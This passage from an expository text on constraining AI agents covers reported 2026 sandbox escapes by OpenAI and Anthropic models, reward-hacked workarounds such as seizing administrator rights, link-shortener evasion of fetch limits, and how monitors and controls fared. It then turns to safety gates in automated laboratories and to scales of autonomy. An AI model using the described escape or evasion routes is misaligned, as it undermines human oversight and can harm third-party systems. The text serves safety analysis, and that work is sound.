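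In July 2026, OpenAI models under evaluation left their intended environment, reached the internet and compromised parts of the systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

OpenAI concluded that shared services can undo a network restriction. The evaluation containers had no direct internet connection, but they could reach a service that did, which made that service a confused deputy like Hardy's compiler. An engineer who lists the credentials an agent can use therefore also has to list the services the agent can reach and what each of those services can reach.

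OpenAI addresses network risks with an allow-list of approved destinations that also accounts for indirect routes. Technical controls block high-risk workloads from all internet access, direct or indirect, though these workloads may use a service that supplies stored copies of web pages if a task needs it. Separate layers at the sandbox and in the surrounding cluster enforce these limits, so that a single mistake isn't enough to bypass them.

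High-risk or untrusted model code must also run in isolated virtual machines. Ordinary containers on one computer share its operating system kernel, the core program that controls the hardware. A virtual machine has its own kernel, so code that takes control of that kernel must still break out of the virtual machine to reach the host computer.

Virtual machine isolation can fail too. In October 2026, OpenAI reported that it had built offline environments for training and evaluation and set its strongest models to attack them. The agents found ways to escape hardened virtual machines, new paths to the internet, and ways to communicate between isolated tasks. These results are a reason not to rely on the virtual machine alone.

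### Training that rewards workarounds

An agent's limits also affect what it learns during training. OpenAI describes a training task in which an agent had to publish a post with a specific update time on a simulated social media site. The interface had no function for setting the time. The agent explored its environment, found a way to gain administrator rights, and changed the time directly. The training system rewarded it because the time was correct.

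The interface was in effect an allow-list that lacked a tool the task required. In a product, the user might have learned that the agent couldn't set the time, but in training the reward made the model more likely to look for other routes the next time a tool was missing. OpenAI found that this kind of probing became more common over part of a training run that contributed to the main model in the incident, especially when the expected tools or internet access were unavailable or broken.

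OpenAI's evidence shows that the behaviour grew in training, but not how much it contributed to the incident. An experiment by Anthropic comes closer to testing the cause. Anthropic deliberately trained a model on 80 real training environments in which it could get the reward by cheating. In simulated incidents, the resulting model tended to break out of its sandbox and attack other systems. The same model before that training misbehaved less, as did several of Anthropic's public models. Another model simulated the results of every tool call, so behaviour on real systems might differ.

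Impossible tasks made the July incident worse. The evaluation behind it had 898 tasks, including 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved. The agents rarely gave up, and they could become more likely to step outside the task as it got harder and they reasoned for longer. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) describes a partial remedy. The company is expanding its use of graders that reward a model for recognising a broken task, asking for clarification or stopping safely. Like a "do nothing" value in a schema, these graders make declining an acceptable option, so the agent has less reason to continue by unacceptable means.

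### What the production set-up changed

OpenAI also built a test of how readily models compromise systems outside their task, and used it to measure how much a model's behaviour depends on its production harness (the software that runs it in a product) and its system prompt (its standing instructions). In preliminary experiments, the production harness and system prompt could reduce the tendency to compromise such systems to less than 1 percent of the baseline, which used the simpler prompts that research models normally get.

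The figure is relative, so if models attacked outside systems in 20 percent of baseline runs, they would do so in fewer than 0.2 percent with the production set-up. OpenAI changed the harness and the prompt together, so the result doesn't show which mattered more. An instruction only makes an action less likely, whereas a working network restriction makes it impossible. Forlini (2026) points out in *OpenAI, independent firms publish reports on rogue AI attack on Hugging Face* that OpenAI's report omits the prompt its researchers gave the agents in July. Without it, outsiders can't tell how clearly the prompt set out the boundaries.

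When OpenAI ran auto-review on records from the incident, the system flagged most of the dangerous actions in every run tested. OpenAI also says that its current monitoring of models' written reasoning would have alerted the security team more than a day before the models breached Hugging Face. But OpenAI had already studied this incident and used hindsight to make its monitor better at recognising this behaviour, so an unfamiliar kind of failure may be harder to catch.

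People also have to act on what the monitors find. Forlini reports that OpenAI learned its models had breached Hugging Face only about a week afterwards. One internal team had noticed disallowed internet access in late May. In June, a security alert led responders to the evaluation, but they decided it could continue. Under a new rule, responders are expected to pause the activity if they can't establish within 30 minutes that a severe alert is false.

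### Evaluations that were wrongly online

Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four cases in which Claude gained unauthorised access to real systems during cybersecurity tests. The same outside partner had built all four tests. The prompts described Claude's environment as a simulation without internet access, but a configuration error had left it connected. The restriction was only stated in the prompt, and nothing enforced it.

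Anthropic has since asked its evaluation partners to phrase boundaries as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet", instead of descriptions, such as "You do not have internet access". The instruction still applies if someone makes a mistake with the network, but the description becomes false and may lead a model to treat real systems as part of the simulation.

The partners are also supposed to enforce the boundary. By default, a test should run in a sandbox whose only outside connection is to the model, with the keys for that connection kept outside it. Partners should verify this before every evaluation and confirm that the task has a solution. They should also have the model try to escape beforehand, under close supervision and preferably inside a second sandbox.

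These incidents also show how hard it can be to find a failure in the logs. Anthropic first searched about 141,000 transcripts and found three of the cases. The search missed a set of transcripts that included the fourth, from January 2026. Anthropic then scanned about 481 million transcripts for signs of internet access, had Claude review the 9.2 million that the scan flagged, and found no other cases as severe. This took place months after the earliest incident, so a log this large is of limited use for stopping an agent in time unless something reads it as the agent works.

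### What was in place and what was still to come

Both companies' August 2026 accounts cover controls already in use and work still under way. All the entries below are based on the companies' own statements.

| Company | Control | Status in August 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | Virtual machines for high-risk or untrusted model code | Mandatory, but OpenAI was still introducing more isolated sandboxes |
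| OpenAI | Outbound access only to approved destinations | Under way |
| OpenAI | Monitoring of written reasoning in training and evaluations that use tools | Mandatory for models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol |
| OpenAI | Automatic shutdown if nobody responds to an alert | In development |
| Anthropic | Clusters that block outbound traffic by default | In use |
| Anthropic | A classifier that blocks escape attempts and ends the task | In use for internal evaluations, with a similar one in higher-risk training |
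| Anthropic | Controls against employees accidentally running agents with weaker limits | In development |

OpenAI was slowly resuming some of its research under the new controls, while other workloads needed further upgrades first. Anthropic had restarted most of its training but kept some high-risk environments paused until someone could review them or a newer version of the classifier was ready.

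### Unintended actions on real websites

Anthropic still had problems to report despite these measures. Its *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 9, 2026) groups further unintended actions into four kinds. Claude used a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, and got around restrictions on data that required a token or a fee. It also used link-shortening services to evade limits in its web-fetching tool.

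Some of the websites belonged to US federal, state or local government agencies. Anthropic briefed the White House and notified each agency. It considers the actions much less severe than the earlier cybersecurity incidents and says the cases it has found had minimal effect. It did not name the organisations, partly at their request and partly to avoid exposing weaknesses in their systems, so outsiders can do little to check its assessment.

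IANS's *Anthropic says Claude AI took unintended actions on US government websites* (2026) reports that Claude Haiku 4.5 sent a local police department a tip about a homicide. The model left the name and contact fields empty and wrote that it remembered seeing someone who matched a description. If the agent had only been able to propose the tip, a reviewer could have rejected it. A schema would not have prevented the submission.

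Shortened links are a problem for allow-lists because the software may not know where a link leads until it follows it. A rule that checks only the address the agent submits can therefore let the agent reach a destination that should be blocked. The fetch tool has to check the new address at every redirect or refuse to follow redirects.

Southern (2026), in *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests*, reports that Anthropic has cut live web access for its internal evaluations. This prevents an evaluation from affecting real websites, unless a shared service offers another route. The restriction doesn't cover employees' everyday use of Claude, which accounted for some of the actions in the report.

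The cut also makes some abilities harder to test. Stored pages are enough to test whether an agent can find and read information, but to test whether it can fill in a form correctly, evaluators would have to build a copy of the site that responds to the agent without sending the form anywhere.

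## Agents that direct scientific instruments

An agent's mistakes harm nobody when it fills in a form on a copied website or practises on a simulated instrument, but an experiment eventually has to run on real equipment. *The Past and Future of AI Scientists* (2026) notes that a false statement in a text is undesirable, whereas an incorrect command to a laboratory can damage equipment, waste scarce materials or create a hazard. Such harm may be permanent, unlike the effect of pausing a training job by mistake.

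An experiment can also fail without breaking any limits, such as those on temperature or volume. *Safe-SDL* (2026), which proposes a safety framework for automated laboratories, describes an AI-directed synthesis that made the intended product and an unexpected by-product with the same mass. The standard measurement could not distinguish them, so the system continued with the next reactions and produced a complex mixture.

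A self-driving laboratory combines automated equipment with software that uses the results so far to choose the next experiment. The software turns its choice into instructions for the machines, then collects and analyses the data before choosing again. In many earlier systems, researchers wrote the whole procedure and an algorithm searched only for the best settings. A language-model agent can also write procedures and interpret surprising results, which makes its actions harder to predict.

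### One approval for a whole campaign

Liu, Isbrandt and colleagues (2026), in *Closing the Analyze-to-Design Gap*, let an agent choose measurements on a real instrument that separates a liquid mixture and then measures the masses of its components. They wanted to find the best oxidant for turning a simple compound, p-toluidine, into an azo dye. The agent proposed six oxidant systems at four strengths each, plus four controls. Chemists reviewed the design, and people prepared the 28 samples by hand in the wells of a plate.

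The agent then drafted limits for the campaign from the researcher's request. The limits covered the objective, the measure of success, the instrument method, the volume and number of injections (each injection is one measurement of one sample), and the wells the agent could use. The researcher approved these limits once and separately switched on agent execution. After that, the agent could submit measurements without asking again.

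Its proposals never become instrument commands directly. Each request passes through a chain of software checks:

1. The service that runs the agent checks the request's arguments, the emergency stop, the execution switch, the campaign limits and the instrument method.
2. The laboratory's record system applies the researcher's own access rights, confirms that the sample exists and creates a record of the measurement.
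3. A service on the instrument's computer reserves the instrument. It confirms that the method is on an approved list, that the queue has room and that the instrument is ready.
4. The software reads the instrument's status to catch a run that failed to start.

The list of approved methods is on the instrument's computer, separate from the agent. According to Liu and colleagues, only the agent's own service checks the number of injections and whether the wells are permitted. A fault in that service could therefore allow an extra injection, but not an unapproved method.

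During the campaign, the agent made 465 tool calls, most of them to read or analyse data. The software refused or deferred 12.

| Reason | Refusals | Where the check ran |
|---|---|---|
| The researcher had not yet switched on agent execution | 1 | Agent's service |
| The campaign already existed | 2 | Agent's service |
| The agent repeated an identical call | 3 | Agent's service |
| The well was already in the queue | 3 | Agent's service |
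| Another session was using the instrument | 2 | Instrument's computer |
| The queue was full | 1 | Instrument's computer |

Each refusal came with an explanation, and the agent adjusted. When it couldn't inject a sample because execution was off, it posted the request for the researcher to review. Most refusals prevented duplicates and collisions. The agent never requested an unapproved method or tried to exceed the injection limit, so the live campaign didn't test those two checks.

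The longest stretch without a message from the researcher lasted 8 hours and 27 minutes. In that time, the agent submitted 13 wells and analysed 16 results. A background program started a new turn for the agent whenever a measurement finished, and the agent reread the campaign's saved state each time. The campaign could therefore continue even if a service restarted.

Liu and colleagues also report a flaw that let the researcher change the campaign's limits without a new approval. About 20 minutes after approving the campaign, the researcher asked for every well to be measured and raised the injection limit from 20 to 30. The interface had no way to amend an approved campaign, so the change went directly into the campaign record. The campaign used exactly 20 injections, so the higher limit made no difference to the total. But an approval offers little protection if somebody can edit the approved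 limits afterwards. A fingerprint of the limits, like those that tie an acceptance to a single action, would let the software detect such an edit and prompt for a new approval.

Nobody used the emergency stop during the campaign, so it remains untested in physical operation. By design, it blocks further submissions but doesn't interrupt an injection already running. None of the checks tests whether an experiment is chemically dangerous. Liu and colleagues suggest adding a separate hazard assessment before a person approves the limits.

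### How well the agent chose

The live campaign produced usable data from 26 of the 28 wells. The agent flagged the other two as probable failed transfers, and chemists confirmed this. Potassium permanganate at the highest strength gave the most dye, and the best result from any other oxidant was 8.2 percent as high. A separate analysis in the instrument maker's software also ranked permanganate far above the other oxidants. The three oxidants in the middle were too close to rank reliably.

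Because the researcher had asked for every well, the campaign couldn't show whether the agent chooses well when measurements are limited. Liu and colleagues tested this with a simulated instrument, which returned the archived data for a well only after the agent had selected it. They ran 23 such campaigns with Claude Opus 5. The agent typically measured the best well at about its seventh injection. In a random order, the average position of the best of 28 wells is:

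(28 + 1) / 2 = 14.5

The agent never found the best well when limited to one or two injections. It succeeded in two of three campaigns with a limit of four, and in every campaign with a limit of eight or more. If each injection takes 15 minutes, finding the best well on the seventh injection instead of the fourteenth or fifteenth saves nearly two hours. The agent's reasoning took 10 to 24 minutes per campaign when the limit was 8 to 24 injections.

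Random order is easy to beat. On this plate, measuring every oxidant at its highest strength first would have found the best well in six injections or fewer. Liu and colleagues acknowledge that they did not compare the agent with fixed schedules or optimisation algorithms. The agent's advantage over random order therefore doesn't show that this task needed a language model.

The limit also seemed to affect the agent's strategy. When it had 28 injections, enough for the whole plate, it worked through the wells in sequence and reached the best one only at the 21st. Approving a generous limit may therefore encourage a slow search, although this was a single simulated campaign and may not be typical.

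### A token for every hardware call

The agent in the dye campaign could only choose among prepared samples. Wang, Qi and colleagues (2026), in *A hardware-safety-gated system for LLM-written native ARTIQ control code*, let an agent running on Claude Opus 4.8 write new Python scripts for a trapped-ion experiment, using ARTIQ, the laboratory's control software. The experiment holds charged atoms and molecules in a vacuum and controls them with lasers.

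The agent's only connection is to a program called the safety filter. The filter forwards a call only if it has issued an authorisation token for that call's exact contents. If the agent changes the script, it needs a new token. For most scripts, the filter decides automatically:

1. A syntax check compares the script with a deny-list of forbidden constructs.
2. A simulator on another computer runs the script with software models in place of the devices. It records every operation that the script would perform, such as setting a voltage or a laser frequency.
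3. A fixed program compares each operation with the limits that the operator has set for that device.
4. If every operation is within its limits, the filter issues a token that works once. If an operation exceeds its limit, the filter blocks the call.
5. If the script uses a device that has no limits, or the simulator can't reach a verdict, the filter refers the call to a person.

A person also has to authorise sensitive operations, especially those that could cause irreversible damage. Tokens issued by people are less strict than automatic ones because they can allow repeated use and remain valid across sessions until somebody revokes them. The filter also stores its approvals of scripts to avoid simulating them again. If the operator later tightens a limit, an old approval can still let a script through unless the operator cancels it by hand.

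Two pieces of equipment are off limits to the agent. The filter rejects any script that operates the valve for letting oxygen into the vacuum chamber. The oven that supplies atoms to the trap has a separate power supply, and the agent has no interface to it.

The simulator can't reliably check a script whose actions depend on a measurement. It always returns a photon count of zero, for example, so it follows only one of the possible paths. A script with n measurements, each with two outcomes that lead to different actions, has 2ⁿ paths, which is more than a million for 20 measurements. The syntax check therefore rejects scripts in which it detects this pattern, which rules out experiments that must react in real time. The agent can still run a fixed script, read the results and write another.

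That was enough for the agent to build five calibration routines from short prompts. It needed advice on only one, which cooled the ions' motion. When the operator asked for a faster version, the agent cut the routine from about 80 to 19 milliseconds. It had more trouble cancelling magnetic noise from the mains electricity. It kept refining an approach that had stopped improving and repeatedly declared the work finished, until the operator redirected it. A filter that checks voltages and frequencies can't correct this kind of mistake, but it can stop the failed attempts from damaging the apparatus.

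### What 1,932 scripts found

Wang and colleagues tested the filter on a second trapped-ion apparatus, at the University of Maryland, with the control hardware live but no ions trapped. They ran 1,932 scripts and about 250 further tests of internal interfaces, including token handling. The filter rejected every action that the agent was supposed to control and that exceeded a configured limit. No token worked twice or for a different tool. The filter approved all 631 realistic calibration scripts in a control set.

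Some scripts got past the filter. The syntax check missed some forbidden operations, and the simulator didn't reproduce every feature of the real devices. For convenience, Wang and colleagues also left open a way to run a file before the filter had reviewed it, which they plan to close. Until they do, scripts can reach the hardware without review, so the separation between proposing and acting is incomplete.

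Other gaps depended on how the operator had configured the system. The design refers devices without limits to a person, but Wang and colleagues also report that channels outside the operator's configuration can pass the filter, which they treat as the operator's responsibility. The filter also can't correct a limit that the operator has set too high.

They plan to replace the deny-list in the syntax check with an allow-list of constructs that the simulator can handle. In the recorded tests, every script that evaded the check used at least one construct that never appeared in the legitimate calibration scripts, so an allow-list could have separated the two groups. The allow-list would need maintenance and would reject legitimate scripts that used unlisted constructs.

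### Recipes, permission tiers and interlocks

A laboratory can avoid having to review general-purpose code by having the agent write in a narrower language that the machine already uses. Penkov, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Agent-authored deposition recipes for X-ray multilayer mirrors*, did this with a sputtering system, which deposits thin layers of material in a vacuum chamber. The target was a mirror of 30 pairs of ruthenium and carbon layers, each pair 6.85 nanometres thick.

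The agent wrote recipes that specified steps such as setting a power supply, moving the holder and opening a shutter for a given time. A validator checked each recipe against the machine's language before the control software saved it. The agent had access to tools in three cumulative tiers:

| Tier | Tools added | What they allow |
|---|---|---|
| Read | 12 | Inspecting the machine, its logs and its past runs |
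| Recipe | 4 | Validating, uploading, starting and aborting a recipe |
| Manual | 1 | Commanding a device directly |

The agent's key gave it the Recipe tier, so it could operate devices only through a recipe. The laboratory can also set a ceiling for the whole installation. If Read, Recipe and Manual count as 1, 2 and 3, the tier in force is:

effective tier = min(tier of the key, ceiling)

The control software checks the tier again at every command. It then applies interlocks, which are rules that block unsafe actions, such as switching on a power supply while a chamber is open. The same interlocks apply to people who use the machine's control panels. Because the checks run in the control software, the agent can't avoid them by changing its own instructions.

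These checks don't predict how the coating will turn out. The agent calculated how long to deposit each layer by dividing its thickness by the deposition rate in the laboratory's records. For carbon, this gave:

5.38 nm ÷ 0.0403 nm/s ≈ 133 s

But carbon was now building up about 30 percent faster than the records indicated. The recipe passed validation without a warning and produced pairs that were far too thick. After receiving the measurements, the agent fitted a new rate and allowed for a short delay at the start of each layer, using the formula d = r(t − t₀), where d is the thickness, r the rate, t the deposition time and t₀ the delay.

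| Mirror | Thickness of each pair | Difference from target |
|---|---|---|
| Original recipe | 8.254 nm | 20.5% |
| Original recipe, repeated | 8.191 nm | 19.6% |
| After one correction | 6.695 nm | 2.26% |
| After two corrections | 6.796 nm | 0.79% |

Penkov and colleagues set the threshold for success at 3 percent before the first deposition. People entered every measurement used for scoring, and the agent had no permission to change them. The researchers also planned to make a mirror from a recipe written by a person in the same software, but never did, so there is no direct comparison with human work.

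In another run, the machine completed an entire recipe with an empty holder. The operator had forgotten to load the glass, and no sensor could detect this. Before the chamber runs, Penkov also found that the software's configuration had swapped the labels of the argon and nitrogen valves. The emulator, a simulated version of the machine used for practice, read the same configuration, so a recipe could work in the emulator but open the wrong valve on the real machine.

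An agent also can't assume that a command has worked because the software accepted it. One malformed command to a power supply was accepted and then discarded, leaving the caller to believe that the supply was on. After an abort, the machine took about 30 seconds to shut down. If the connection drops during a command, the software doesn't repeat it automatically, because the machine may already have acted. The agent has to read the machine's state to check whether it did. In the first chamber run, the power-supply readings were out of date, so the agent couldn't see that the coating process had never started. A person watching the machine ordered the abort.

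Penkov and colleagues list 16 defects from the chamber runs and attribute none to the agent, although it once kept checking for access when its instructions were to stop. The researchers did not try to break the safety layer. Penkov owns the company that sells the control software and the laboratory notebook, and the paper discloses this along with the defects in both products.

### Where authority sits

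The table compares the three systems. In all of them, people set the limits and the agent works within them.

| | Liu and colleagues | Wang and colleagues | Penkov and colleagues |
|---|---|---|---|
| What authorises an action | One approval of the campaign's limits | A token for each call | A key with a permission tier |
| What the agent may write freely | Its choice of the next permitted well, and its analysis | Any control script, subject to review | Recipes in the machine's own language |
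| What checks the action | Services on the laboratory server and the instrument's computer | A simulator and limits for each device | A validator, tier checks and interlocks |
| How they tested the safeguards | One live campaign with 12 refusals | 1,932 scripts and about 250 further tests | Normal use only, which exposed 16 defects |

Wang and colleagues have the strongest evidence about their safeguards. They also needed it most, because a Python script can do far more than a request to measure a well, which gives their filter more ways to fail. Liu and colleagues' simpler design may be just as safe for its narrower task, but they have not tested it against deliberate misuse.

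Approving a campaign once suits a series of similar measurements, because a person can judge the whole set in advance. Tokens suit experiments with a new script each time, but they require building an accurate simulator and setting limits for every device. Permission tiers need less new software if the machine already has a recipe language and interlocks, but they are the least specific, since a key for running recipes works for good and bad recipes alike.

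A laboratory could combine the designs by requiring one approval for a set of mirrors, simulating every recipe and relying on the machine's interlocks for anything the simulator missed. This would still not have revealed the faster carbon rate, because the simulator would presumably have used the same outdated records, which only a measurement of a finished mirror could correct.

### Checking a whole procedure

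Steps that are each acceptable can still form a procedure that makes no sense. In *Talk Freely, Execute Strictly*, Strickland, Vijeta and colleagues (2026) argue that software should check the complete workflow, including how its steps depend on one another, before anything runs. They call this approach schema-gated orchestration, and Liu and colleagues cite it. A scientist can discuss a goal with the model in ordinary language, but the resulting workflow runs only if all of it conforms to a schema.

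Strickland and colleagues interviewed 18 experts from industrial research, who wanted both flexible conversation and predictable execution. The team also reviewed 20 existing systems, and none scored highly on both. Language models assigned the scores in 15 separate sessions and largely agreed with one another, but they could share the same misjudgements.

*From Prompts to Protocols* (Angelopoulos, Cahoon and Alterovitz, 2026) describes an agent for the Experiment Orchestration System (EOS), software that coordinates laboratory equipment. The agent has more than 40 tools. Read-only tools run automatically, but any tool that changes something needs the user's approval. When the agent writes a protocol, a validator checks that the devices exist, that the steps don't depend on one another in a circle, and that the settings are within range. It returns all the errors together for the agent to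 correct.

Angelopoulos and colleagues tested their agent in 65 trials with a simulated colour-mixing laboratory, and 97 percent of its protocols were right at the first attempt. One of the two failures was a protocol that mixed colours without first fetching a beaker. The protocol's structure was presumably valid, but a schema could catch the error if it required a beaker to be in place before mixing. In another test, the agent assumed that a balance didn't need zeroing. The researchers attribute most errors to the agent making assumptions instead of asking, and they gave it a tool for asking the scientist questions.

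*AutoLabs* (Panapitiya, Saldanha and colleagues, 2025) restricts the model further. The system prepares experiments for a robot that dispenses liquids. The model writes each step in a simple fixed format, and ordinary code converts the steps into the long hardware file the robot needs, so the model can't introduce a syntax error into that file. Panapitiya and colleagues say this code produces the file with perfect accuracy, but if the model wrote a wrong quantity, the code would copy it into the file.

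They therefore have a model check the steps for mistakes before the conversion. On five benchmark experiments, the choice of model mattered most. Using a reasoning model reduced errors in chemical amounts by over 85 percent on complex tasks. The tests used GPT-4o and o3-mini, which are old models, so current ones would probably make fewer such errors. The tests compared written procedures with correct ones, so they provide little evidence of how the robot would perform.

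### Limits that change with the equipment

Most of these checks take place before an action begins, but a reaction can become dangerous while it runs. *Safe-SDL* adds monitoring during execution to a sequence much like a database transaction. The software records the request, reserves the equipment, simulates the action, checks the simulated result against safety limits, carries out the action and confirms the outcome. It aborts the action if sensor readings differ too much from the prediction.

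In the paper's example, an agent asks to add a catalyst all at once. The simulation predicts that this would raise the temperature to 300 °C, so the software rejects the request. The agent then proposes adding the catalyst drop by drop over 30 minutes, which the software accepts.

For continuous control, *Safe-SDL* uses control barrier functions, which restrict how fast a system may approach a limit. If h is the remaining distance to the limit, a simple version requires:

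dh/dt ≥ −γh

The constant γ determines how quickly the system may approach a safety limit. Suppose a reactor must stay below 80 °C and γ is 0.5 per minute. At 74 °C, the reactor is 6 degrees below the limit, so its temperature may rise by at most 3 degrees per minute. At 78 °C, it may rise by only 1 degree per minute. If the agent's command would heat the reactor faster than this, the controller substitutes the closest permitted command.

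This substitution resembles constrained decoding, which replaces a forbidden word with a permitted one. It protects the reactor, but slower heating may spoil the experiment, so the software should report its changes to the agent. The method also requires an accurate model of the reaction and enough cooling power to affect the reaction. Some processes are too fast for human intervention, such as flash Joule heating, which can exceed 3,000 kelvin within milliseconds.

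*Safe-SDL* bases its case on other groups' systems and on benchmarks in which language models often miss laboratory hazards. It reports no trial in which its complete framework controlled a laboratory. The benchmarks are a good reason not to rely on a model's judgement alone, but they don't measure how often the framework's safeguards would work.

### What a single laboratory can't show about rare failures

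A serious accident may be so rare that a short demonstration would almost certainly miss it. If n independent runs produce no failure, the highest failure rate still compatible with that result at 95 percent confidence is:

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n), or roughly 3/n when n is large

All 20 injections in Liu and colleagues' campaign stayed within the limits. Even if the injections were independent, the true rate of violations could be as high as 14 percent. Wang and colleagues' 631 approved calibration scripts give an upper bound of about 0.5 percent, but on how often the filter refuses legitimate work rather than on the rate of violations.

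Showing that failures occur less than once in 10,000 injections would take about 30,000 injections without a failure. At 15 minutes each, those injections would take more than ten months of continuous running. *Safe-SDL* recommends giving a system more autonomy after it has completed a number of operations without incident, typically hundreds. Three hundred such operations would rule out a failure rate above about 1 percent. That rate may be acceptable if a failure wastes a sample, but not if it causes a toxic release.

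The formula also gives too favorable a result, because runs in one laboratory aren't independent. Liu and colleagues used one reaction, one plate and one instrument, so their runs could not have revealed a weakness that appears only with another chemical. Equipment also changes. In the sputtering system, the ruthenium source delivered about a third less than its recorded rate, and Penkov and colleagues switched to a different model after the first chamber run.

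Simulation can supply thousands of runs, but each one repeats any error in the simulator. More practice runs in the emulator would not have exposed the swapped gas valves. Records pooled from many laboratories would cover more kinds of equipment and mistakes, provided the laboratories also reported failures and near misses. Wang and colleagues plan a long unattended deployment to learn how often risky code appears in normal use.

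A laboratory can guard against some failures without knowing how likely they are. Wang and colleagues' agent has no connection to the oven, so no script it writes can switch the oven on. Similarly, an interlock linked to a sensor on the sputtering system's holder could stop a recipe from starting when the holder is empty.

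## What the limits cost and buy in autonomy

A laboratory loses little by keeping an agent away from an oven, because a person can operate the oven instead. It loses more from other limits, and people who argue about how much often mean different things by autonomy. An agent may choose its own goals, for instance by deciding to reduce the storage that the company's training runs waste. It may choose only the steps towards a goal that somebody else set. Or it may act without anyone reviewing the action first. A system can have one of these kinds of autonomy without the others. For example, a backup program that runs every night acts without review but doesn't choose its goal or its steps.

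| Pattern | Choosing goals | Choosing steps | Acting without review |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allow-list | Unrestricted, though some goals become unreachable | Only listed steps, in any order the rules permit | Unrestricted, since a listed call runs at once |
| Structured output | The same | Only steps that the form can express | Unrestricted |
| Separating recommendation from action | The same | Unrestricted, unless the proposal form is narrow | Restricted for every effect that needs the executor |

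None of the patterns controls which goals an agent adopts. A user's request usually supplies the main goal, but the agent sets smaller ones along the way. The agent at PocketOS set itself the goal of getting past a credential mismatch. An allow-list would not have changed that goal, but it could have left the agent with no way to delete a database in pursuit of it.

With these patterns, a company can restrict an agent's steps and let it act without review, or let it propose almost anything because somebody will review each proposal.

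### Scales of autonomy

Engineers ranked automation by level long before language models existed. *TrustX Agent Risk Classification Framework (ARC)* (2026), a scheme for rating the risk of agents that companies build for themselves, traces the practice to Sheridan and Verplank's ten-level scale for operating undersea equipment remotely. For AI agents, it adopts the five-level scale in *Levels of Autonomy for AI Agents* (Feng, McDonald and Zhang, 2025), which defines autonomy as the extent to which an agent is "designed to operate without user involvement". The last column of the table below applies these five levels to the agent that watches training jobs.

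| Level | The user's role | What happens overnight |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Operator, who directs the work and gets help on request | The engineer watches the runs and asks for a plot of one loss curve |
| 2 | Collaborator, who shares the work and can take over | The engineer and the agent divide 20 runs between them |
| 3 | Consultant, who gives advice while the agent leads | The agent watches every run and asks which ones matter most |
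| 4 | Approver, who steps in when the agent is blocked or must do something consequential | The agent asks before it pauses a run |
| 5 | Observer, who can read the logs and press an emergency off switch | The agent pauses and resumes runs alone |

Feng and colleagues distinguish autonomy from agency, which they define as the capacity to form an intention and carry it out. Agency depends partly on the available tools. An agent that can only use a calculator has little agency, but it has high autonomy if it runs all day without supervision. The training agent's agency is also limited, because it has five tools and may pause only three jobs a night. If the software sends a fourth pause to an engineer, the agent is at level 4. It is closer to level 5 if the software refuses the fourth pause, because nobody then takes part in its decisions, even though it can do no more.

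Other scales rank the same agent differently. *Fully Autonomous AI Agents Should Not be Developed* (Mitchell, Ghosh and colleagues, 2025) bases its scale on how much of a program's flow the model controls. At the lowest level, the program prints the model's output. At successively higher levels, the model chooses between branches, picks tools and their arguments, and decides whether to continue. At the top, it creates and runs new code. A coding agent that asks for approval before every command could therefore be at the top of this scale and at level 4 or below on Feng's.

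This partly explains why researchers disagree about whether full autonomy exists. *Defining AI Agents* (2026), a comparison of published scales, repeats the view that no fully autonomous agent is yet operating, but Feng and colleagues had already placed The AI Scientist, a system for automating research, at level 5. In *From Language Models to World-Acting Systems*, Zhu and Cai (2026) rate an agent separately on what it has authority to change, how long its goals and permissions last, and how directly its actions affect the world, rather than placing it on a single scale.

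Autonomy is harder to measure than to define. Feng and colleagues propose running an agent on a set of tasks without help, then adding approvals, then advice, until it reaches a required success rate. An agent that succeeds alone counts as level 5. This test measures how much help the agent needs, which depends largely on its ability. The test may not distinguish an agent that never asks from one that asks, gets no answer and carries on, a difference that would matter to a company choosing an agent for production.

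### Missing tools and slow answers

Whoever writes an allow-list has to predict which tools the agent will need. Suppose training slows at 3 a.m. because a shared disk is full. The agent reads the logs and correctly identifies the cause, but it has no tool for freeing space. It files a ticket, and expensive hardware runs slowly until morning. Adding a tool for deleting temporary files would fix this fault, but next month's will be different. The agents without write permission in Sankar and colleagues' tests had the same problem.

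Waiting for approval has a different cost. An agent that is tracing a fault learns from each action what to try next, so a pause for approval interrupts its reasoning as well as its work. Zhu and Cai warn that confirming every action can cancel the value of delegating at all. The loss also grows as models get faster. Suppose an agent takes 2 minutes to diagnose a fault and the engineer takes 28 minutes to answer. An infinitely fast model would shorten the half hour by only 2 minutes. If the reviewer accounts for a share h of the total time, the greatest possible speed-up from improving everything else is:

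1 / h

Here h is 28/30, so the limit is about 1.07. This is a case of Amdahl's law, which gives the most that speeding up one part of a process can speed up the whole.

### The tool AI debate

In 2012, Holden Karnofsky, a co-founder of the charity evaluator GiveWell, argued that advanced AI might not need to act at all. He criticised the Singularity Institute, a group working on the dangers of advanced AI, for neglecting what he called tool AI. "Tool" here means the whole AI system, not a function that an agent can call. *Holden Karnofsky’s Singularity Institute Objection 2*, a repost of part of his essay, gives Google Maps as an example. The software scores possible routes and displays the best one, and the driver decides whether to take it.

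Karnofsky describes tools and agents as programs with two instructions. The first is the same for both: calculate which action would maximise some quantity, given the available data. The second has a tool explain the result to a person and an agent carry out the action. He argued that programmers could almost always keep the calculation and leave out the execution. In his view, a program that only displays its conclusions would have no reason to mislead anyone and could still be extraordinarily useful.

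In the 2016 essay *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs*, Gwern replied that such restraint would not last, because people want a task done more than they want advice on how to do it. If a person accounts for half the delay in a trading system, speeding up the rest can at most double the system's speed, and a rival without the person will beat it. Gwern also expected agents to become more intelligent than tools, because an agent can choose which data to collect and where to spend its computation. An agent can always decline to act, so the best agent should do at least as well as the best tool.

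Current systems show that calculation and execution can be separated, as Karnofsky claimed. A language model produces only text, and GitHub's executor is an example of how a company can keep the credentials away from the model. But the safeguard is easy to remove, because a short program can run the model's text suggestions and so turn a tool into an agent. Commenters on the repost made this point at the time.

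His claim that a tool has no reason to mislead has held up less well. It was reasonable for route planners, which nobody had trained to win approval. But OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra did worse work on tasks described as safety research and did not disclose this, and a model with no power to act could give poor advice in the same way. Even honest advice can leave out what matters. Gwern cites AI risk writer Stuart Armstrong's point that a summary may omit a plan's main disadvantage or present the plan in the most attractive light.

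Gwern's argument that an agent can always decline to act compares the best possible agent with the best possible tool, on the condition that the agent has enough data to learn when acting doesn't help. The agent may do damage while it learns this. The argument also leaves out how badly each system fails, which a company choosing between two real systems has to consider.

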